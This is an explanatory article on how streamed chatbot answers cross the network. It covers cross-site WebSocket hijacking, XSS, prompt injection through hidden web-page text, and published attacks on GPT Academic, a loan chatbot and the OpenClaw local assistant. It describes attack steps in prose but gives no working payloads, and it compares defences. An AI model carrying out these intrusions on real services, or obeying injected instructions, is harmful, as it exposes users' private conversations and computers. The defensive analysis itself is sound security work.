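# Web-application vulnerabilities in chatbots that stream model output to the browser

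## How does a chatbot's answer travel from the server to the page?

A web chatbot has two parts, a front end and a server. The front end runs in the user's browser and consists of the page, its scripts and its connection to the server. The server stores the accounts and saved conversations, passes each question to a language model and returns the answer. Most chatbots return the answer while the model is still writing it, so the browser holds a connection open, receives the answer as many small pieces of text and adds each piece to the page. Web-application vulnerabilities, most of which are older than chatbots, are flaws in these two parts rather than in the model. For example, a server might accept a connection from the wrong website, or a page might run part of an answer as program code.

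A language model produces its answer one text token at a time, and a token is often only part of a word. The server can wait and send the finished answer, or it can stream the tokens to the browser as the model produces them. KodeKloud's *How to Stream LLM Responses Token by Token With Server Sent Events* timed both methods on the same task. The whole answer took 7.9 seconds either way, but the first word appeared after 0.1 seconds with streaming and after 7.9 seconds without it. Streaming saves no computing time, but nearly everyone uses it because it shortens the wait for the first word.

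### Four ways to stream

The simplest method is a plain HTTP stream. HTTP is the protocol of ordinary web pages, in which the browser sends a request and the server sends a response. The server can leave the response open and write to it bit by bit, while a script in the page reads whatever has arrived. The developers have to invent their own way to mark where one piece ends and the next begins.

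Server-sent events (SSE) supply that missing format. They are a one-way stream of messages from server to browser over an ordinary HTTP response. One piece of an answer might look like this, with a blank line to end it:

```
event: piece
data: {"text": " 90"}

```

Browsers have a built-in reader for such streams, EventSource. According to *Server-sent events*, by WHATWG, the group that maintains the HTML standard, EventSource reconnects automatically after a break and reports the last event it received, so that the server can resume from there. But a script can give it only an address and one setting about cookies, which leaves no room for a long prompt. Developers work around this in two ways. *AI Token Streaming* shows a script that sends the prompt in an HTTP POST request and reads the events from the response without EventSource, so it loses the automatic reconnection. *AI token streaming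 isn't about SSE vs WebSockets* describes a POST request that returns only a stream's identifier, after which the page connects to that stream separately.

A WebSocket is a connection that starts as an HTTP request and then stays open for messages in both directions. Fette and Melnikov (2011) wrote the standard, *The WebSocket Protocol* (RFC 6455), with games, stock tickers and shared editing in mind. Until then, developers of such applications had made the browser repeatedly request updates from the server. Over a WebSocket, either side can send a message at any time. The protocol marks where each message ends and whether it holds text or binary data, but it adds very little else and does not define users, conversations or permissions.

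Socket.IO is a library that sends named events, such as "ask" or "stop", between browser and server, usually over a WebSocket. It can use repeated HTTP requests when a WebSocket is not available. The event names are a convenience for developers, and anyone who controls the browser can send any of the events.

Many chatbots stream answers without a WebSocket. OpenAI, Anthropic, Cohere and Hugging Face all stream their models' output over SSE, according to tianpan.co's *SSE vs WebSockets vs gRPC Streaming for LLM Apps* (2026), and Stream, a vendor of chat software, adds that the developer kits of OpenAI, Anthropic and Vercel read SSE too. But this describes only the connection between the model provider and the chatbot's server. In the usual route, described in Railway's *Stream AI Responses to a Frontend with Server-Sent Events*, the front end sends the prompt to the application's server,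 which calls the model provider and forwards each piece of the answer to the front end. The server can forward those pieces over a different transport from the one the provider used.

For the final connection to the browser, the choice between SSE and WebSocket depends mostly on whether the user has something to send while the answer is still arriving. Railway's *Choose Between SSE and WebSockets* recommends SSE where the browser only listens, and gives streamed model output as the most common case. CallSphere, which sells chat and voice agents, uses SSE for its healthcare and salon-booking chats, and considers WebSocket the only realistic choice for a voice agent that callers can interrupt. These vendors describe their own practice rather than chatbots in general, but they agree that typed question-and-answer products tend to use SSE, while products with live audio, interruption or several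 participants tend to use WebSocket.

### One question at chat.example

A hypothetical chatbot at chat.example uses a WebSocket. Its owner lets shops embed it in their own pages, which affects its cookies.

A user logs in with a name and password. The server creates a session, a record that this browser belongs to this user, and sends the browser a cookie holding the session's identifier:

```
Set-Cookie: session=4be1c07a; Secure; HttpOnly; SameSite=None
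```

A cookie is a short string that the browser stores and attaches to later requests to the same server. The Secure attribute restricts it to encrypted connections, and the HttpOnly attribute stops scripts in the page from reading it. The developers could instead have given the page an access token, a secret string that proves who a user is. The browser attaches a cookie automatically, whereas a script has to add an access token explicitly.

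The page loads, and its script asks the browser for a WebSocket to chat.example. The browser sends the first half of the handshake, the HTTP request and response that open the connection:

```
GET /ws HTTP/1.1
Host: chat.example
Origin: https://chat.example
Cookie: session=4be1c07a
Connection: Upgrade
Upgrade: websocket
Sec-WebSocket-Key: q0mVxT2hYbJ9cR4nLw8eZg==
Sec-WebSocket-Version: 13
```

Under WHATWG's *WebSockets*, which governs the browser's side, a script opening a connection supplies only an address and, optionally, the names of subprotocols (conventions for what the messages mean). The browser fills in the rest of the request, including the Origin header, which identifies the site whose script asked for the connection. No script, hostile or not, can change that header or add others, so a page with an access token has to send it some other way. Include Security's *Cross-Site WebSocket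 Hijacking Exploitation in 2025* (2025) mentions sending it in the subprotocol field or in the first message after the connection opens.

The server looks up the session and replies with status 101, "Switching Protocols". It also joins the browser's Sec-WebSocket-Key to a fixed string, hashes the result, and returns the hash, which the browser checks before it opens the connection. This exchange proves only that the server understood a WebSocket request. PortSwigger's *Cross-site WebSocket hijacking* warns that the key plays no part in authentication. It is easy to assume otherwise because the key looks random.

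Now the user types a question about the temperature at which water boils at 3,000 metres. The front end wraps the question in a message with a type and a conversation number, and sends it. Messages carry no HTTP headers, so neither the cookie nor the Origin header travels with them; the server remembers whose connection this is from the handshake. It forwards the question to the model provider and relays the answer in a dozen messages, of which these are the first three:

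```
{"type": "piece", "chat": 58, "text": "About"}
{"type": "piece", "chat": 58, "text": " 90"}
{"type": "piece", "chat": 58, "text": " °C,"}
```

The browser hands each message to the page's script, which adds the text to what is already on the screen, so the reader sees "About", then "About 90", then "About 90 °C,". If the script assigns the text to an element's textContent property, the browser displays every character literally, but if it uses innerHTML, the browser reads the text as HTML, the language of web pages, and creates whatever elements the text describes. The *HTML5 Security Cheat Sheet* recommends textContent for messages that one page receives from another, and the same reasoning applies to messages from a socket. Chatbots rarely use textContent alone, however, because users want headings, lists and links, which models write in a light notation called Markdown and the front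 end turns into HTML.

When the answer is complete, the server saves it with the question. If the user later reopens the transcript or shares it with a colleague, the front end turns the same text into page content again, perhaps in the colleague's browser.

### What one site may do to another

Meanwhile, the user may have other, possibly hostile, pages open. Browsers keep pages apart by origin, which is the combination of scheme, host and port that identifies a site, such as https://chat.example. CS 161's university textbook, *Same-Origin Policy*, explains that the browser compares these parts as strings. So http://chat.example is a different origin because its scheme differs, and https://help.chat.example is a different origin because its host differs.

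The same-origin policy is a browser rule that stops a page on one origin from reading another origin's data. If a hostile page at https://quiz.example requests the user's saved conversations from chat.example, the browser may send the request but withholds the response from the page's script. PortSwigger's *Same-origin policy (SOP)* points out that the response could contain private data, because the browser may attach the user's cookie to the request. A server can relax the rule through Cross-Origin Resource Sharing (CORS), a set of response headers that name the origins allowed to read the response.

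W3C's *Same Origin Policy* describes the rule broadly as letting one origin send to another but not receive from it, and sending alone can do harm. In cross-site request forgery, a hostile page makes the visitor's browser send a request that the target server treats as the visitor's own. For example, a page at quiz.example might contain a hidden form that posts to the address at chat.example for deleting all conversations. The browser attaches the session cookie and the server deletes them, even though quiz.example cannot read the response. Bingler, West and Wilander (2025), in *Cookies*, trace the problem to "ambient authority", in which the browser supplies the user's proof of identity with a request to an address the attacker chose. *Cookies* is the revised cookie standard, which the IESG approved on 2 December 2025 (*Protocol Action*, 2025).

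The SameSite setting on a cookie limits this. With Strict, the browser sends the cookie only with requests that come from the same site. Lax also lets the browser send it when a user follows a link to the site. None removes the limit. Google's *Cookie attributes* gives Lax as the default for a cookie without the setting, but Include Security found that Chrome and Edge apply this default while Firefox and Safari do not, and that those two restrict cookies from other sites by different means. The default does not protect chat.example, whose developers chose None because a chatbot inside a shop's page is an embedded widget. Bingler and colleagues list such widgets, along with some single sign-on systems, among the uses that need None.

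SameSite also allows cookies on requests between different origins within the same site. web.dev's *SameSite cookies explained* defines a site by the domain suffix and the name just before it, so help.chat.example and chat.example are two origins but one site. An attacker who can run a script on the help pages can therefore send requests to the chatbot with even a Strict cookie attached.

### Why a WebSocket escapes the same-origin policy

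The browser at least protects the reply to an ordinary request, but it does not protect replies sent over a WebSocket. A script on quiz.example can ask for a connection to chat.example, and the browser will send the handshake shown above with only the Origin header changed, to https://quiz.example. If chat.example answers with status 101, the script can send messages and read every reply.

WHATWG gives the WebSocket handshake its own request mode, "websocket", and tells the browser to include cookies, subject to the SameSite setting. In a comment on that mode, Adam Rice states that the browser sends no preflight, the advance request that asks a server's permission for some cross-origin requests. When the response arrives, the browser checks the status, the upgrade headers, the computed value and any extensions or subprotocol, but it does not check for a header that allows quiz.example to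 read the reply. *Cross-Site WebSocket Hijacking (CSWSH)* (Schneider, 2013), which gave the resulting attack its name, describes this as the reverse of the CORS default, since a WebSocket delivers the reply to the script even if the server has not given the permission that CORS would require. MITRE's public catalogue of software weaknesses also lists WebSockets as exempt from both the same-origin policy and CORS.

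Fette and Melnikov deliberately left the server to decide which origins may connect, and they adopted the Origin header, which a separate standard defines, for this purpose. They recommend that a server meant only for certain sites verify the header and refuse unwelcome origins with status 403, and they warn that a server without such a check "will accept connections from anywhere". Because the check is only recommended, a server that ignores the header still completes a valid handshake. Developers used to the browser's protection may never notice that they have to provide their own.

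The standard also leaves the login method to the server, which can use cookies or any other mechanism that works over HTTP. It requires both ends to validate the data they receive, but it defines no message types, so only the application's developers can know which messages are valid. A program outside the browser can send any Origin header it likes, so checking the header protects a visitor from hostile pages but does not verify who the visitor is.

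If chat.example had used SSE, the script on the hostile page at quiz.example could not have read the stream unless chat.example allowed it, because EventSource requests go through CORS. Cross-site request forgery would still be possible on the requests that carry the prompts.

### When the text itself is hostile

Everything so far concerns who can use the connection. The text that comes through it can also be an attack, whichever transport carries it.

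Cross-site scripting (XSS) is a flaw that lets an attacker's script run in a page with that page's origin and access. Suppose chat.example inserts conversation titles through innerHTML, and someone shares a conversation whose title contains HTML with a script in it. The script then runs in the browser of anyone who opens the conversation. This is stored XSS because chat.example saved the title. HttpOnly keeps the script from reading the user's cookie, but the script can open its own WebSocket without reading it. The browser will send the cookie and a genuine Origin header of https://chat.example, which the server's check will accept.

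Prompt injection is the placing of text where a model will read it, so that the model follows the attacker's instructions. For example, a user might ask chat.example to summarise a web page that contains an instruction, hidden in white text on a white background, to end every summary with a particular piece of HTML. If the model follows it, the attacker has written part of the answer without connecting to chat.example. Whether this does any harm in the browser depends on how the front end inserts the answer into the page. If it uses innerHTML without filtering, the prompt injection becomes XSS. If it uses textContent, the user just sees some odd characters at the end of the summary.

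The trace therefore contains four points at which somebody has to decide what to trust:

| Decision | Where it falls at chat.example | If the developers leave it out |
|---|---|---|
| Who may connect | The server compares the Origin header with a list during the handshake | A page on any site can try to open the socket with the visitor's cookie |
| Who is speaking | The server ties the connection to a session or an access token | Strangers can use the chatbot, or a connection can outlive its login |
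| Which messages to accept | Server and front end check the type, content and permissions of each message | A sender can name someone else's conversation or trigger a hidden function |
| What the page does with the text | The front end displays it literally or turns it into HTML | Text from a model or another user can run as script |

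## Can another website open the chatbot's socket?

If chat.example does not check the Origin header, any page the user visits can use the chatbot's WebSocket in the user's name. Security researchers call this cross-site WebSocket hijacking. The attack works without the user's password and does not depend on a mistake by the model.

### The attack on chat.example

A user logs in to chat.example and closes the tab without logging out, so the session cookie stays in the browser. Later, the user follows a link to https://quiz.example. A script on that page opens a WebSocket to chat.example, and the browser attaches the session cookie to the handshake. The server finds a valid login, accepts the connection and treats every message sent over it as the user's own.

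The script must also send messages that the server accepts. The attacker can learn these beforehand by opening an account at chat.example and watching the traffic in their own browser. The script requests the list of saved conversations, receives their titles and numbers, then fetches the conversations one by one and forwards each to a server the attacker controls. The user sees only a quiz during this time, and although closing the page normally ends the connection, the script may already have copied the whole history.

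The attacker's script opens a new connection rather than seizing one the user already has, as the word "hijacking" might suggest. If the user has chat.example open in another tab, that tab keeps working as before.

In ordinary cross-site request forgery, the attacker can't read the server's replies. A hidden form at quiz.example could delete all the user's conversations, but the attacker would need to know a conversation's number in advance to delete only that one. Over a WebSocket, the attacker can read each reply and use it to write the next message. PortSwigger notes that sometimes the attacker only has to wait for private data to arrive. Hyland's *Can’t Stop, Won’t Stop Hijacking (CSWSH) WebSockets* demonstrates the attack on a practice site with a live chat. The hostile page sends "READY", and the server returns the chat history, which includes the victim's username and password.

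A chatbot's history can be just as revealing, since people paste contracts, medical questions and source code into their chats. The attacker can also use the bot's capabilities. If chat.example's bot can look up orders or send email, the script can send it a message requesting either action. This doesn't require prompt injection, because the request arrives as a message from the user, so training the model not to follow instructions in web pages doesn't prevent it.

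An attacker can also use a WebSocket to bypass protection that works elsewhere in the same application. Include Security tested a large web application whose server accepted ordinary requests only if they declared their content to be JSON. That declaration makes a browser send a preflight first, so a hostile page could not forge the requests. But the application offered the same functions through a WebSocket, which has no preflight, and through it the testers could make any call as the victim, including deleting the victim's account.

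### What has to line up

Include Security gives three conditions for the attack: the application identifies its users by a cookie, the cookie has SameSite=None, and the server does not verify the source of the connection, either by checking the Origin header or in some other way.

The combination is more common than Include Security expected, and the firm guesses at several reasons. Many applications still use cookies. Login services often span several origins, which forces their developers to set SameSite=None and rely on random tokens in HTTP requests to prevent forgery. The developers do not extend those tokens to the WebSocket handshake. Popular server libraries, such as ws for Node.js, also do not require an Origin check.

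One recent example among libraries is the Python developer kit for the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting models to tools. Its WebSocket component had no way to restrict origins, according to GCVE's *Common Weakness Enumeration*, part of a public database of vulnerabilities. The maintainers had already deprecated the component when they added an origin check in version 1.28.1, in 2026.

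The flaw's prevalence is hard to estimate. Hyland reports finding it in every application with meaningful WebSocket functions that came up in penetration tests. In one, a hostile page could take over a government worker's connection and perform administrative tasks. In another, a second flaw in the socket of an administrators' site let the hostile page run commands on the server. These reports reflect one tester's experience and don't include a count. GCVE listed 77 vulnerabilities under "Missing Origin Validation in WebSockets" by October 2026, but a few of them, such as one in Apache Helix, concern plain HTTP.

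The first two conditions are also narrower than they need to be, because the browser can supply any proof of identity the server accepts, though this is usually a cookie. RabbitMQ, a program that passes messages between applications, did not check the Origin header on two of its WebSocket interfaces. If an administrator configured it to accept a certificate stored in the user's browser, which the browser presents automatically, a hostile page could connect as that user.

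Include Security writes that the attack works only if the cookie's SameSite attribute is None. That is true for a page on another site, but a hostile script at help.chat.example counts as being on the same site as the chatbot, so its attack can work with other SameSite values too.

### What browsers block

In April 2025, Include Security reviewed its past findings and found that some were no longer exploitable because of browser changes. To check the details, the firm built a small server that set a SameSite=None cookie and logged any cookies that arrived with a request or a WebSocket handshake. It then tried attacks from a second domain in several browsers. Logging at the server matters because Chrome's developer tools do not always show the cookies in a WebSocket handshake, so a tester who looks only there may wrongly conclude that the browser sent none.

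SameSite=Lax blocks the attack from another site because the browser sends the cookie when a user follows a link from that site, but not when a script there opens a socket. Chrome treats cookies with no SameSite setting as Lax, except that for two minutes after a site sets one, Chrome also sends it with certain form submissions from other sites. This exception doesn't help the attacker, because a WebSocket handshake is not a form submission.

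Firefox's Total Cookie Protection keeps a separate cookie store for each site the user visits. When quiz.example tries to open a socket to chat.example, Firefox looks in the store for quiz.example, which does not contain the cookie from the user's own visit to the chatbot. The handshake therefore goes out without that cookie, and the server cannot identify the user. This works even for SameSite=None cookies, although users can switch the protection off.

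The three past findings fared differently:

- In 2021 the firm had found a document editor whose cookie had no SameSite setting. The attack then worked in Firefox but not in Chrome. By 2025 it worked in no major browser.
- The application with the JSON requests used SameSite=None. The attack no longer worked in Firefox with its default settings but still worked in Chrome and Edge.
- A network camera accepted anyone on the same private network without a login. A hostile website could still watch its video through the browser of someone on that network, in every browser.

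Cookie restrictions could not protect the camera because it didn't use cookies. Include Security had expected Chrome to block the attack through its check on requests from public sites to private addresses, but that check relied on preflight requests, which WebSocket connections don't send. Chrome has since switched to permission prompts for such access.

The application with the JSON requests is the closest of the three to chat.example, so Chrome's treatment of SameSite=None cookies matters most. Google had planned for years to block third-party cookies, which belong to a site other than the one in the address bar. But on 22 April 2025, in *Next steps for Privacy Sandbox and tracking protections in Chrome*, Chavez (2025) announced that Chrome would keep its existing approach and not add a new prompt about them. Only Incognito mode blocks them by default. Chavez referred to the decision as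 settled that October in *Update on Plans for Privacy Sandbox Technologies*, and MDN's *Third-party cookies* still described Chrome this way in September 2026. The MDN page also listed Safari as having protections similar to Firefox's by default. Little has therefore changed since the tests, and a chatbot with a SameSite=None cookie and no Origin check remains open to attack in an ordinary Chrome window.

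Hyland writes that Firefox, like Chrome, treats a missing SameSite setting as Lax, but Include Security found that Mozilla tried this default and dropped it because too many sites broke. Both agree that Total Cookie Protection stops cross-site WebSocket hijacking in Firefox anyway. According to TechSpot's *Chrome's new security feature could make stolen session cookies virtually useless* (2026), a Chrome feature targets attackers who copy a session cookie and load it into another browser. It does not address cross-site WebSocket hijacking, in which the cookie never leaves the victim's browser.

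### GPT Academic

GPT Academic is an open-source chatbot interface for reading and writing research papers. GCVE's record *CVE-2024-10956*, published on 20 March 2025, describes cross-site WebSocket hijacking in version 3.83. A hostile page could delete the victim's conversation history. According to the record, the causes were weak WebSocket authentication and a missing Origin check.

The record describes hijacking "an existing WebSocket connection", but a page cannot access a connection that another site's page has opened. SentinelOne's *CVE-2024-10956* gives a more plausible sequence, in which the hostile page opens a new socket, the browser attaches the victim's session cookies, and the script sends the command to delete the history. This is a security vendor's reconstruction rather than the original finding. The record gives no cookie settings, so it does not show which browsers the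 attack would have worked in.

Huntr, the bug-bounty platform that registered the flaw, scored its severity at 7.6 out of 10, and the US National Vulnerability Database scored it at 7.1. Both rate the damage to the victim's data as high but the loss of confidentiality as low. The low rating is a little surprising because the connection is two-way and, according to SentinelOne, the attacker could also read replies, within the limits of the messages the application defines. Those messages may reveal little, or the finder may have demonstrated only deletion.

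The US cybersecurity agency CISA noted that a proof of concept existed but did not mark the flaw as actively exploited. The record lists every version up to "latest" as affected and no fixed release. The record may just be out of date, so anyone who runs GPT Academic should test whether their copy rejects connections from a foreign Origin.

### The loan chatbot

SpiderLabs, a team of penetration testers at the security company Trustwave, found a chatbot on a loan application's website that exposed much more sensitive data. Banerjee (2023) published the case on Trustwave's site on 11 May 2023. LevelBlue, which bought Trustwave, hosts an undated copy of the post, *Rendezvous with a Chatbot*.

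The chatbot opened its WebSocket as soon as the page loaded, before the visitor had typed anything. It did so in four steps:

1. The source code of the page contained a fixed access token.
2. The front end sent this in an HTTP request and received a second access token.
3. The front end presented the second access token in an Authorization header and received the address of a WebSocket stream.
4. The front end connected to that address. The server did not check the Origin header.

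The visitor identified themselves only after that, by giving a first name, the last four digits of a US Social Security number and a postal code. The chatbot offered hints when a detail was wrong and repeated personal details in its replies. The access token remained valid for an hour. SpiderLabs found that the chatbot's second socket, used for speech, was also vulnerable.

The testers demonstrated the attack with a page that connected to the stream and waited. Personal data from a conversation then arrived at a server they controlled. LevelBlue's post explains that the hostile page connects from the victim's browser, and the chatbot treats the connection as part of the victim's session.

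That explanation does not fit the rest of the post, which reports that the chatbot used an Authorization header rather than cookies. Browsers do not attach access tokens automatically, so a hostile page in the victim's browser would send nothing that identified the victim. It could copy the fixed access token from the page source and repeat the four steps, but it would presumably get a new stream that nobody else was using.

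The post doesn't explain how the hostile page came to share someone else's stream, though it contains some clues. It describes the attacker waiting for "any customer who uses that stream", which suggests that several visitors could share one. This might happen if the server chose the conversation by an access token that was the same for everyone. In that case an attacker could have listened from anywhere, without luring a victim to a hostile page. The post also reports that the application revealed access keys, usernames and loan data to people who had not logged in, and that this made the hijack easier, so perhaps the attacker could find a victim's stream address in that data. Or the testers may have copied the address of their own stream into the hostile page. That would show that the server accepted a second listener from a foreign origin, but not how an attacker would get a customer's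 stream address.

On any of these readings, the server's main fault was letting a second client join a conversation without checking that it belonged to the same user. The missing Origin check made this possible from a web page, but a program outside the browser could have sent any Origin header. The demonstration is good evidence that the stream leaked, but weaker evidence that a customer would have lost data just by visiting a hostile website.

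LevelBlue's post recommends creating the access token and the stream after the chat session opens, and adding an Origin check and protection against request forgery. It also notes that the chatbot did not start a separate session after the visitor gave their details. This seems the more important point, because if the server had issued a new access token and a new stream once it had identified the customer, anyone who had joined the old stream would have been left with an empty conversation.

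An attacker might have been able to guess the required details without opening the chatbot's socket from another website. The last four digits of a Social Security number have only 10,000 possible values, first names and postal codes are easy to find, and the chatbot helped when a guess was wrong. The testers also bypassed the application's CAPTCHA, a puzzle meant to block automated guessing, by changing a setting in the page.

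### Comparing the fixes

Include Security considers an Origin check the best defence. The server has to compare the whole header with its list of permitted origins. A check that only tests whether the header starts with "https://chat.example" would also accept https://chat.example.quiz.example, which belongs to the attacker.

The origins the list must include depend on how the chatbot is embedded. If a shop shows the chatbot in a frame loaded from chat.example, the handshake carries chat.example's own origin, and one entry is enough. If the shop loads the chatbot as a script in its own page, the handshake carries the shop's origin, so the list has to include every shop that does this. A hostile script on any of those shops' pages will then pass the check.

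Several recent flaws arose in servers that had an Origin check or a setting for one:

- Taipy, a Python framework for web applications, configured its Socket.IO server to accept every origin, with the user's credentials. GCVE's record of September 2026 rates this at 9.3 out of 10.
- Next.js, another web framework, had a check on a WebSocket used during development that an origin of "null" could bypass, as GCVE recorded in March 2026. Browsers send "null" when a page has no ordinary origin, and Hyland's test page did so because Hyland had opened it from a file on disk.
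- Punk, a Perl framework, ran its check only on addresses meant for WebSockets. Under newer versions of HTTP, a handshake could reach other addresses too, and a hostile page could find out which of them responded successfully.

Developers can test the server's Origin check by replaying a handshake with a different Origin. Hyland does this with Burp Suite, a program that intercepts and edits web traffic. If the server completes the handshake and answers messages as usual, the check is missing or broken. An attacker can use the same kind of program to send an allowed Origin, so the server still needs a login to keep out strangers.

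A one-time ticket protects the socket because a hostile page cannot obtain one. Before opening the socket, the front end at chat.example sends an ordinary HTTP request for a ticket. The server checks the user's session, generates a long random string, stores it with the session and returns it. The front end then puts the ticket in the WebSocket URL or the subprotocol field. The server looks up the ticket, deletes it to prevent reuse, and completes the handshake. A script at quiz.example can make the browser request a ticket, but the same-origin policy stops the script from reading the response.

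This protection therefore depends on the server's CORS settings. If chat.example allows any origin to read its responses with the user's cookies attached, quiz.example can read the ticket and use it. A ticket in a URL may also end up in server logs, so it should expire within seconds. A ticket proves only what the server checked when issuing it. The loan chatbot used two access tokens in sequence, but anyone could copy the first from the page source, so having the second proved nothing about the visitor.

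If the front end authenticates in its first message, the server completes the handshake for anyone but does nothing until it receives an access token. A hostile page can open the connection but has no token to send. RabbitMQ's missing Origin check, for example, was harmless in the default configuration, where each client sends its credentials in a message after connecting. It became dangerous only when an administrator chose a method in which the browser supplies the credentials.

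The method fails if the server also accepts a cookie from the handshake as a fallback, or sends any private data before the first message arrives. It also lets unauthenticated clients hold connections open, so the server needs a short time limit and a cap on such connections. The page's script must be able to read the access token, so an attacker who exploits an XSS flaw can copy the token and use it from another computer. An HttpOnly cookie can't be copied this way.

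Hyland also recommends setting the cookie's SameSite attribute to Lax or Strict. This adds a useful second defense for a chatbot that runs only on its own site, but it prevents the embedded use that led chat.example to choose None. Include Security advises against relying on SameSite alone, since a developer might later change it to None for an unrelated reason and reintroduce the vulnerability without noticing. Encryption does not help, because a hostile page can open an encrypted connection as easily as a genuine page can. GCVE nevertheless lists encrypted WebSockets among the mitigations for this weakness.

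The fixes differ in which attackers they stop, but none stops a script already running in chat.example's own page, because that script can send the right Origin, request a ticket and read an access token.

| Fix | A page at quiz.example | A hostile script at help.chat.example | A program outside the browser, without a login |
|---|---|---|---|
| Origin allowlist | Stopped | Stopped, unless the list includes that origin | Not stopped, because it can forge the header |
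| One-time ticket, issued only after login | Stopped, unless CORS lets the page read the ticket | Stopped, with the same exception | Stopped |
| Access token in the first message | Stopped, if the server ignores cookies | Stopped, on the same condition | Stopped |
| SameSite=Lax or Strict | Stopped | Not stopped, because it is the same site | Not stopped, because only browsers apply the setting |

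## Can a website reach an assistant running on the visitor's own computer?

Some assistants run on the user's own computer instead of a company's server. The user still controls them through a web page, but the server behind that page runs on the same computer and usually accepts connections only from programs there. This stops strangers on the internet from connecting directly, but a website the user visits often can connect, because its scripts run in the user's browser, which is one of those programs.

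In February 2026, researchers published two attacks of this kind on OpenClaw, an open-source assistant formerly called Clawdbot and Moltbot. In both, a user who opened a malicious web page could give an attacker control of the assistant and, through it, the computer.

### Why localhost is reachable

Every computer has a loopback address, normally 127.0.0.1, that leads back to the computer itself. Its usual name is localhost. A program that listens only on this address can't receive a connection from another machine.

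Suppose someone running such a program opens https://quiz.example, and a script on the page requests a WebSocket connection to localhost. The visitor's browser makes the connection, so "localhost" means the visitor's computer, not the quiz's server. The connection reaches the local program from 127.0.0.1, just as it would from the program's own page. Only the Origin header, which the browser sets to https://quiz.example, distinguishes the two. If the program doesn't check that header, an attacker who controls the quiz page can carry out cross-site WebSocket hijacking against a server they could not reach from their own computer.

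In OpenClaw, the local program is a WebSocket server called the gateway. According to Oasis Security's *OpenClaw Vulnerability* (2026), the gateway checks logins, stores settings, manages chat sessions and runs the assistant. Phones and other computers can register with it and offer abilities such as reading contacts or running commands. The user logs in with a password or an access token and gives instructions from a terminal or a web page called the Control UI. By default the gateway listens only on localhost, and its developers assumed that local connections could be trusted.

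OpenClaw gained over 100,000 GitHub stars in five days. Stars are bookmarks rather than installations, so they do not show how many computers were exposed.

### A link that gave away the access token

depthfirst's *1-Click RCE To Steal Your OpenClaw Data and Keys (CVE-2026-25253)* (2026), published by a security company on 1 February, describes an attack that began with a link. The Control UI needs to know which gateway to use, and it could take the gateway's address from a parameter in its own link. When the page opened, it did three things:

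1. It read the gateway address from the link and saved it without checking it.
2. It connected to that address immediately.
3. It sent the stored access token in the message that logged it in.

Each step is reasonable if the address is genuine. But an attacker could set up a WebSocket server, put its address in a link to the user's own Control UI, and receive the access token as soon as the user opened the link. The user did not have to type or approve anything. A hostile website could also open the link in a background window.

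Requiring an access token in a WebSocket's first message usually keeps hostile pages out, but OpenClaw's front end, the Control UI, would send its token to any server named in a link. The token went directly to the attacker's server, so an Origin check at the gateway could not have prevented the theft.

An attacker with the stolen access token could log in from anywhere if the user had made the gateway available on the internet. Most users had not, so depthfirst looked for a way to reach localhost and found that the gateway accepted WebSockets from any origin. The hostile page could therefore open a second connection from the victim's browser to OpenClaw's default port on localhost, 18789, and log in with the token.

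The maintainers' advisory, reproduced in GitLab's *CVE-2026-25253* (2026), warns that a gateway listening only on localhost was still vulnerable because the victim's browser makes the outbound connection. That connection explains how the attacker could steal the access token, but using the token against such a gateway from a web page also depended on the gateway not checking the Origin header.

Once logged in, the attacker had administrator rights and could read private data, act through the user's connected accounts and run commands on the computer. OpenClaw could ask the user before running a dangerous command and could confine commands to a sandbox, but an administrator could turn off both protections through the gateway. depthfirst notes that these protections were meant to limit a misbehaving agent. They did little against an attacker who could change the settings without involving the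 model.

The maintainers fixed the flaw in version 2026.1.29, released on 30 January, according to The Hacker News' *OpenClaw Bug Enables One-Click Remote Code Execution via Malicious Link* (2026). The Control UI now asks for confirmation before it connects to a new gateway address. The update cannot undo an earlier leak of an access token, so depthfirst also advises users who suspect a leak to replace their token. MITRE's *CVE-2026-25253* (2026) includes CISA's assessment that a proof of concept existed, and rates the technical impact as total.

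### Guessing the password from a web page

The attack that Oasis Security published on 26 February did not require a stolen access token. The page simply guessed the password. OSV's *GHSA-jmmg-jqc7-5qf4* (2026), a copy of OpenClaw's advisory in a public vulnerability database, attributes the flaw to three behaviours:

- The gateway did not check the Origin header for some kinds of client other than the Control UI, and a hostile page could connect as one of these.
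- The limit on wrong passwords did not apply to connections from localhost.
- The gateway could register a new device from localhost without asking the user.

Oasis Security suggests that the developers made exceptions for localhost because OpenClaw's terminal program, companion app and dashboard all connect from there, and that they probably did not consider that a website's script could do so too. The gateway did not log failed guesses from localhost, so a user who checked the logs would have found no trace of them.

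In Oasis Security's demonstration, a page on an unrelated website guessed the password, logged in with full permissions and exchanged messages with the assistant, with nothing on the screen to alert the user.

Oasis Security writes that any website could silently take full control, but OpenClaw's advisory describes the flaw as "serious, but conditional". The gateway had to use a password rather than an access token, the user had to open a hostile page, and the password had to be one that the attacker could guess in a feasible time. How much that last condition protects people depends on the speed of guessing. Oasis Security measured "hundreds" of guesses per second from a script in the browser. At 300 per second, the times are:

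| What the attacker tries | Number of guesses | Time to try them all |
|---|---|---|
| A list of common passwords | 10,000 | 33 seconds |
| A large dictionary | 1,000,000 | 56 minutes |
| Every value of a random 128-bit access token | 3.4 × 10³⁸ | 3.6 × 10²⁸ years |

Oasis Security states that a script would exhaust a list of common passwords in under a second. At 300 guesses per second, this is true only if the list has fewer than 300 passwords, and even at 900 per second, a list of 1,000 would take more than a second. The statement that a large dictionary would take "only minutes" is more accurate. At 300 guesses per second, the script could try 180,000 passwords in ten minutes, though a million would take nearly an hour.

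Even with these corrections, a weak password offers little protection. Half a minute is an ordinary length for a visit to a web page, and people leave tabs open for much longer than an hour. An attacker would also try the most common passwords first and often succeed well before the end of the list.

If the gateway had allowed only five wrong guesses per minute, trying the list of 10,000 would have taken about 33 hours instead of 33 seconds. A random 128-bit access token hardly needs such a limit, because a search at full speed would still take more than a billion billion times the age of the universe.

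The maintainers released a fix within 24 hours, in version 2026.2.25. The gateway now checks the Origin header for other clients that connect directly from a browser, limits their wrong guesses even when they come from localhost, and no longer silently registers a device for a web page other than the Control UI. A page's script can't alter the Origin header, so the gateway can now distinguish web pages from the user's terminal program, even though both connect from 127.0.0.1.

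The flaw's severity scores depend partly on whether a connection from localhost counts as local. NVD's *CVE-2026-32025 Detail* lists a score of 7.5 out of 10 from the security company VulnCheck, which treats the flaw as one that an outsider can exploit over a network. OSV also gives a score of 5.7 under the same version of the scoring system. That score is based on a local attacker who already has some access, and on no loss of confidentiality. The higher score fits the demonstration better, since Oasis Security's page started with no access and could read the gateway's settings and logs. The lower score seems to treat a connection from localhost as local, which is the assumption that caused the flaw.

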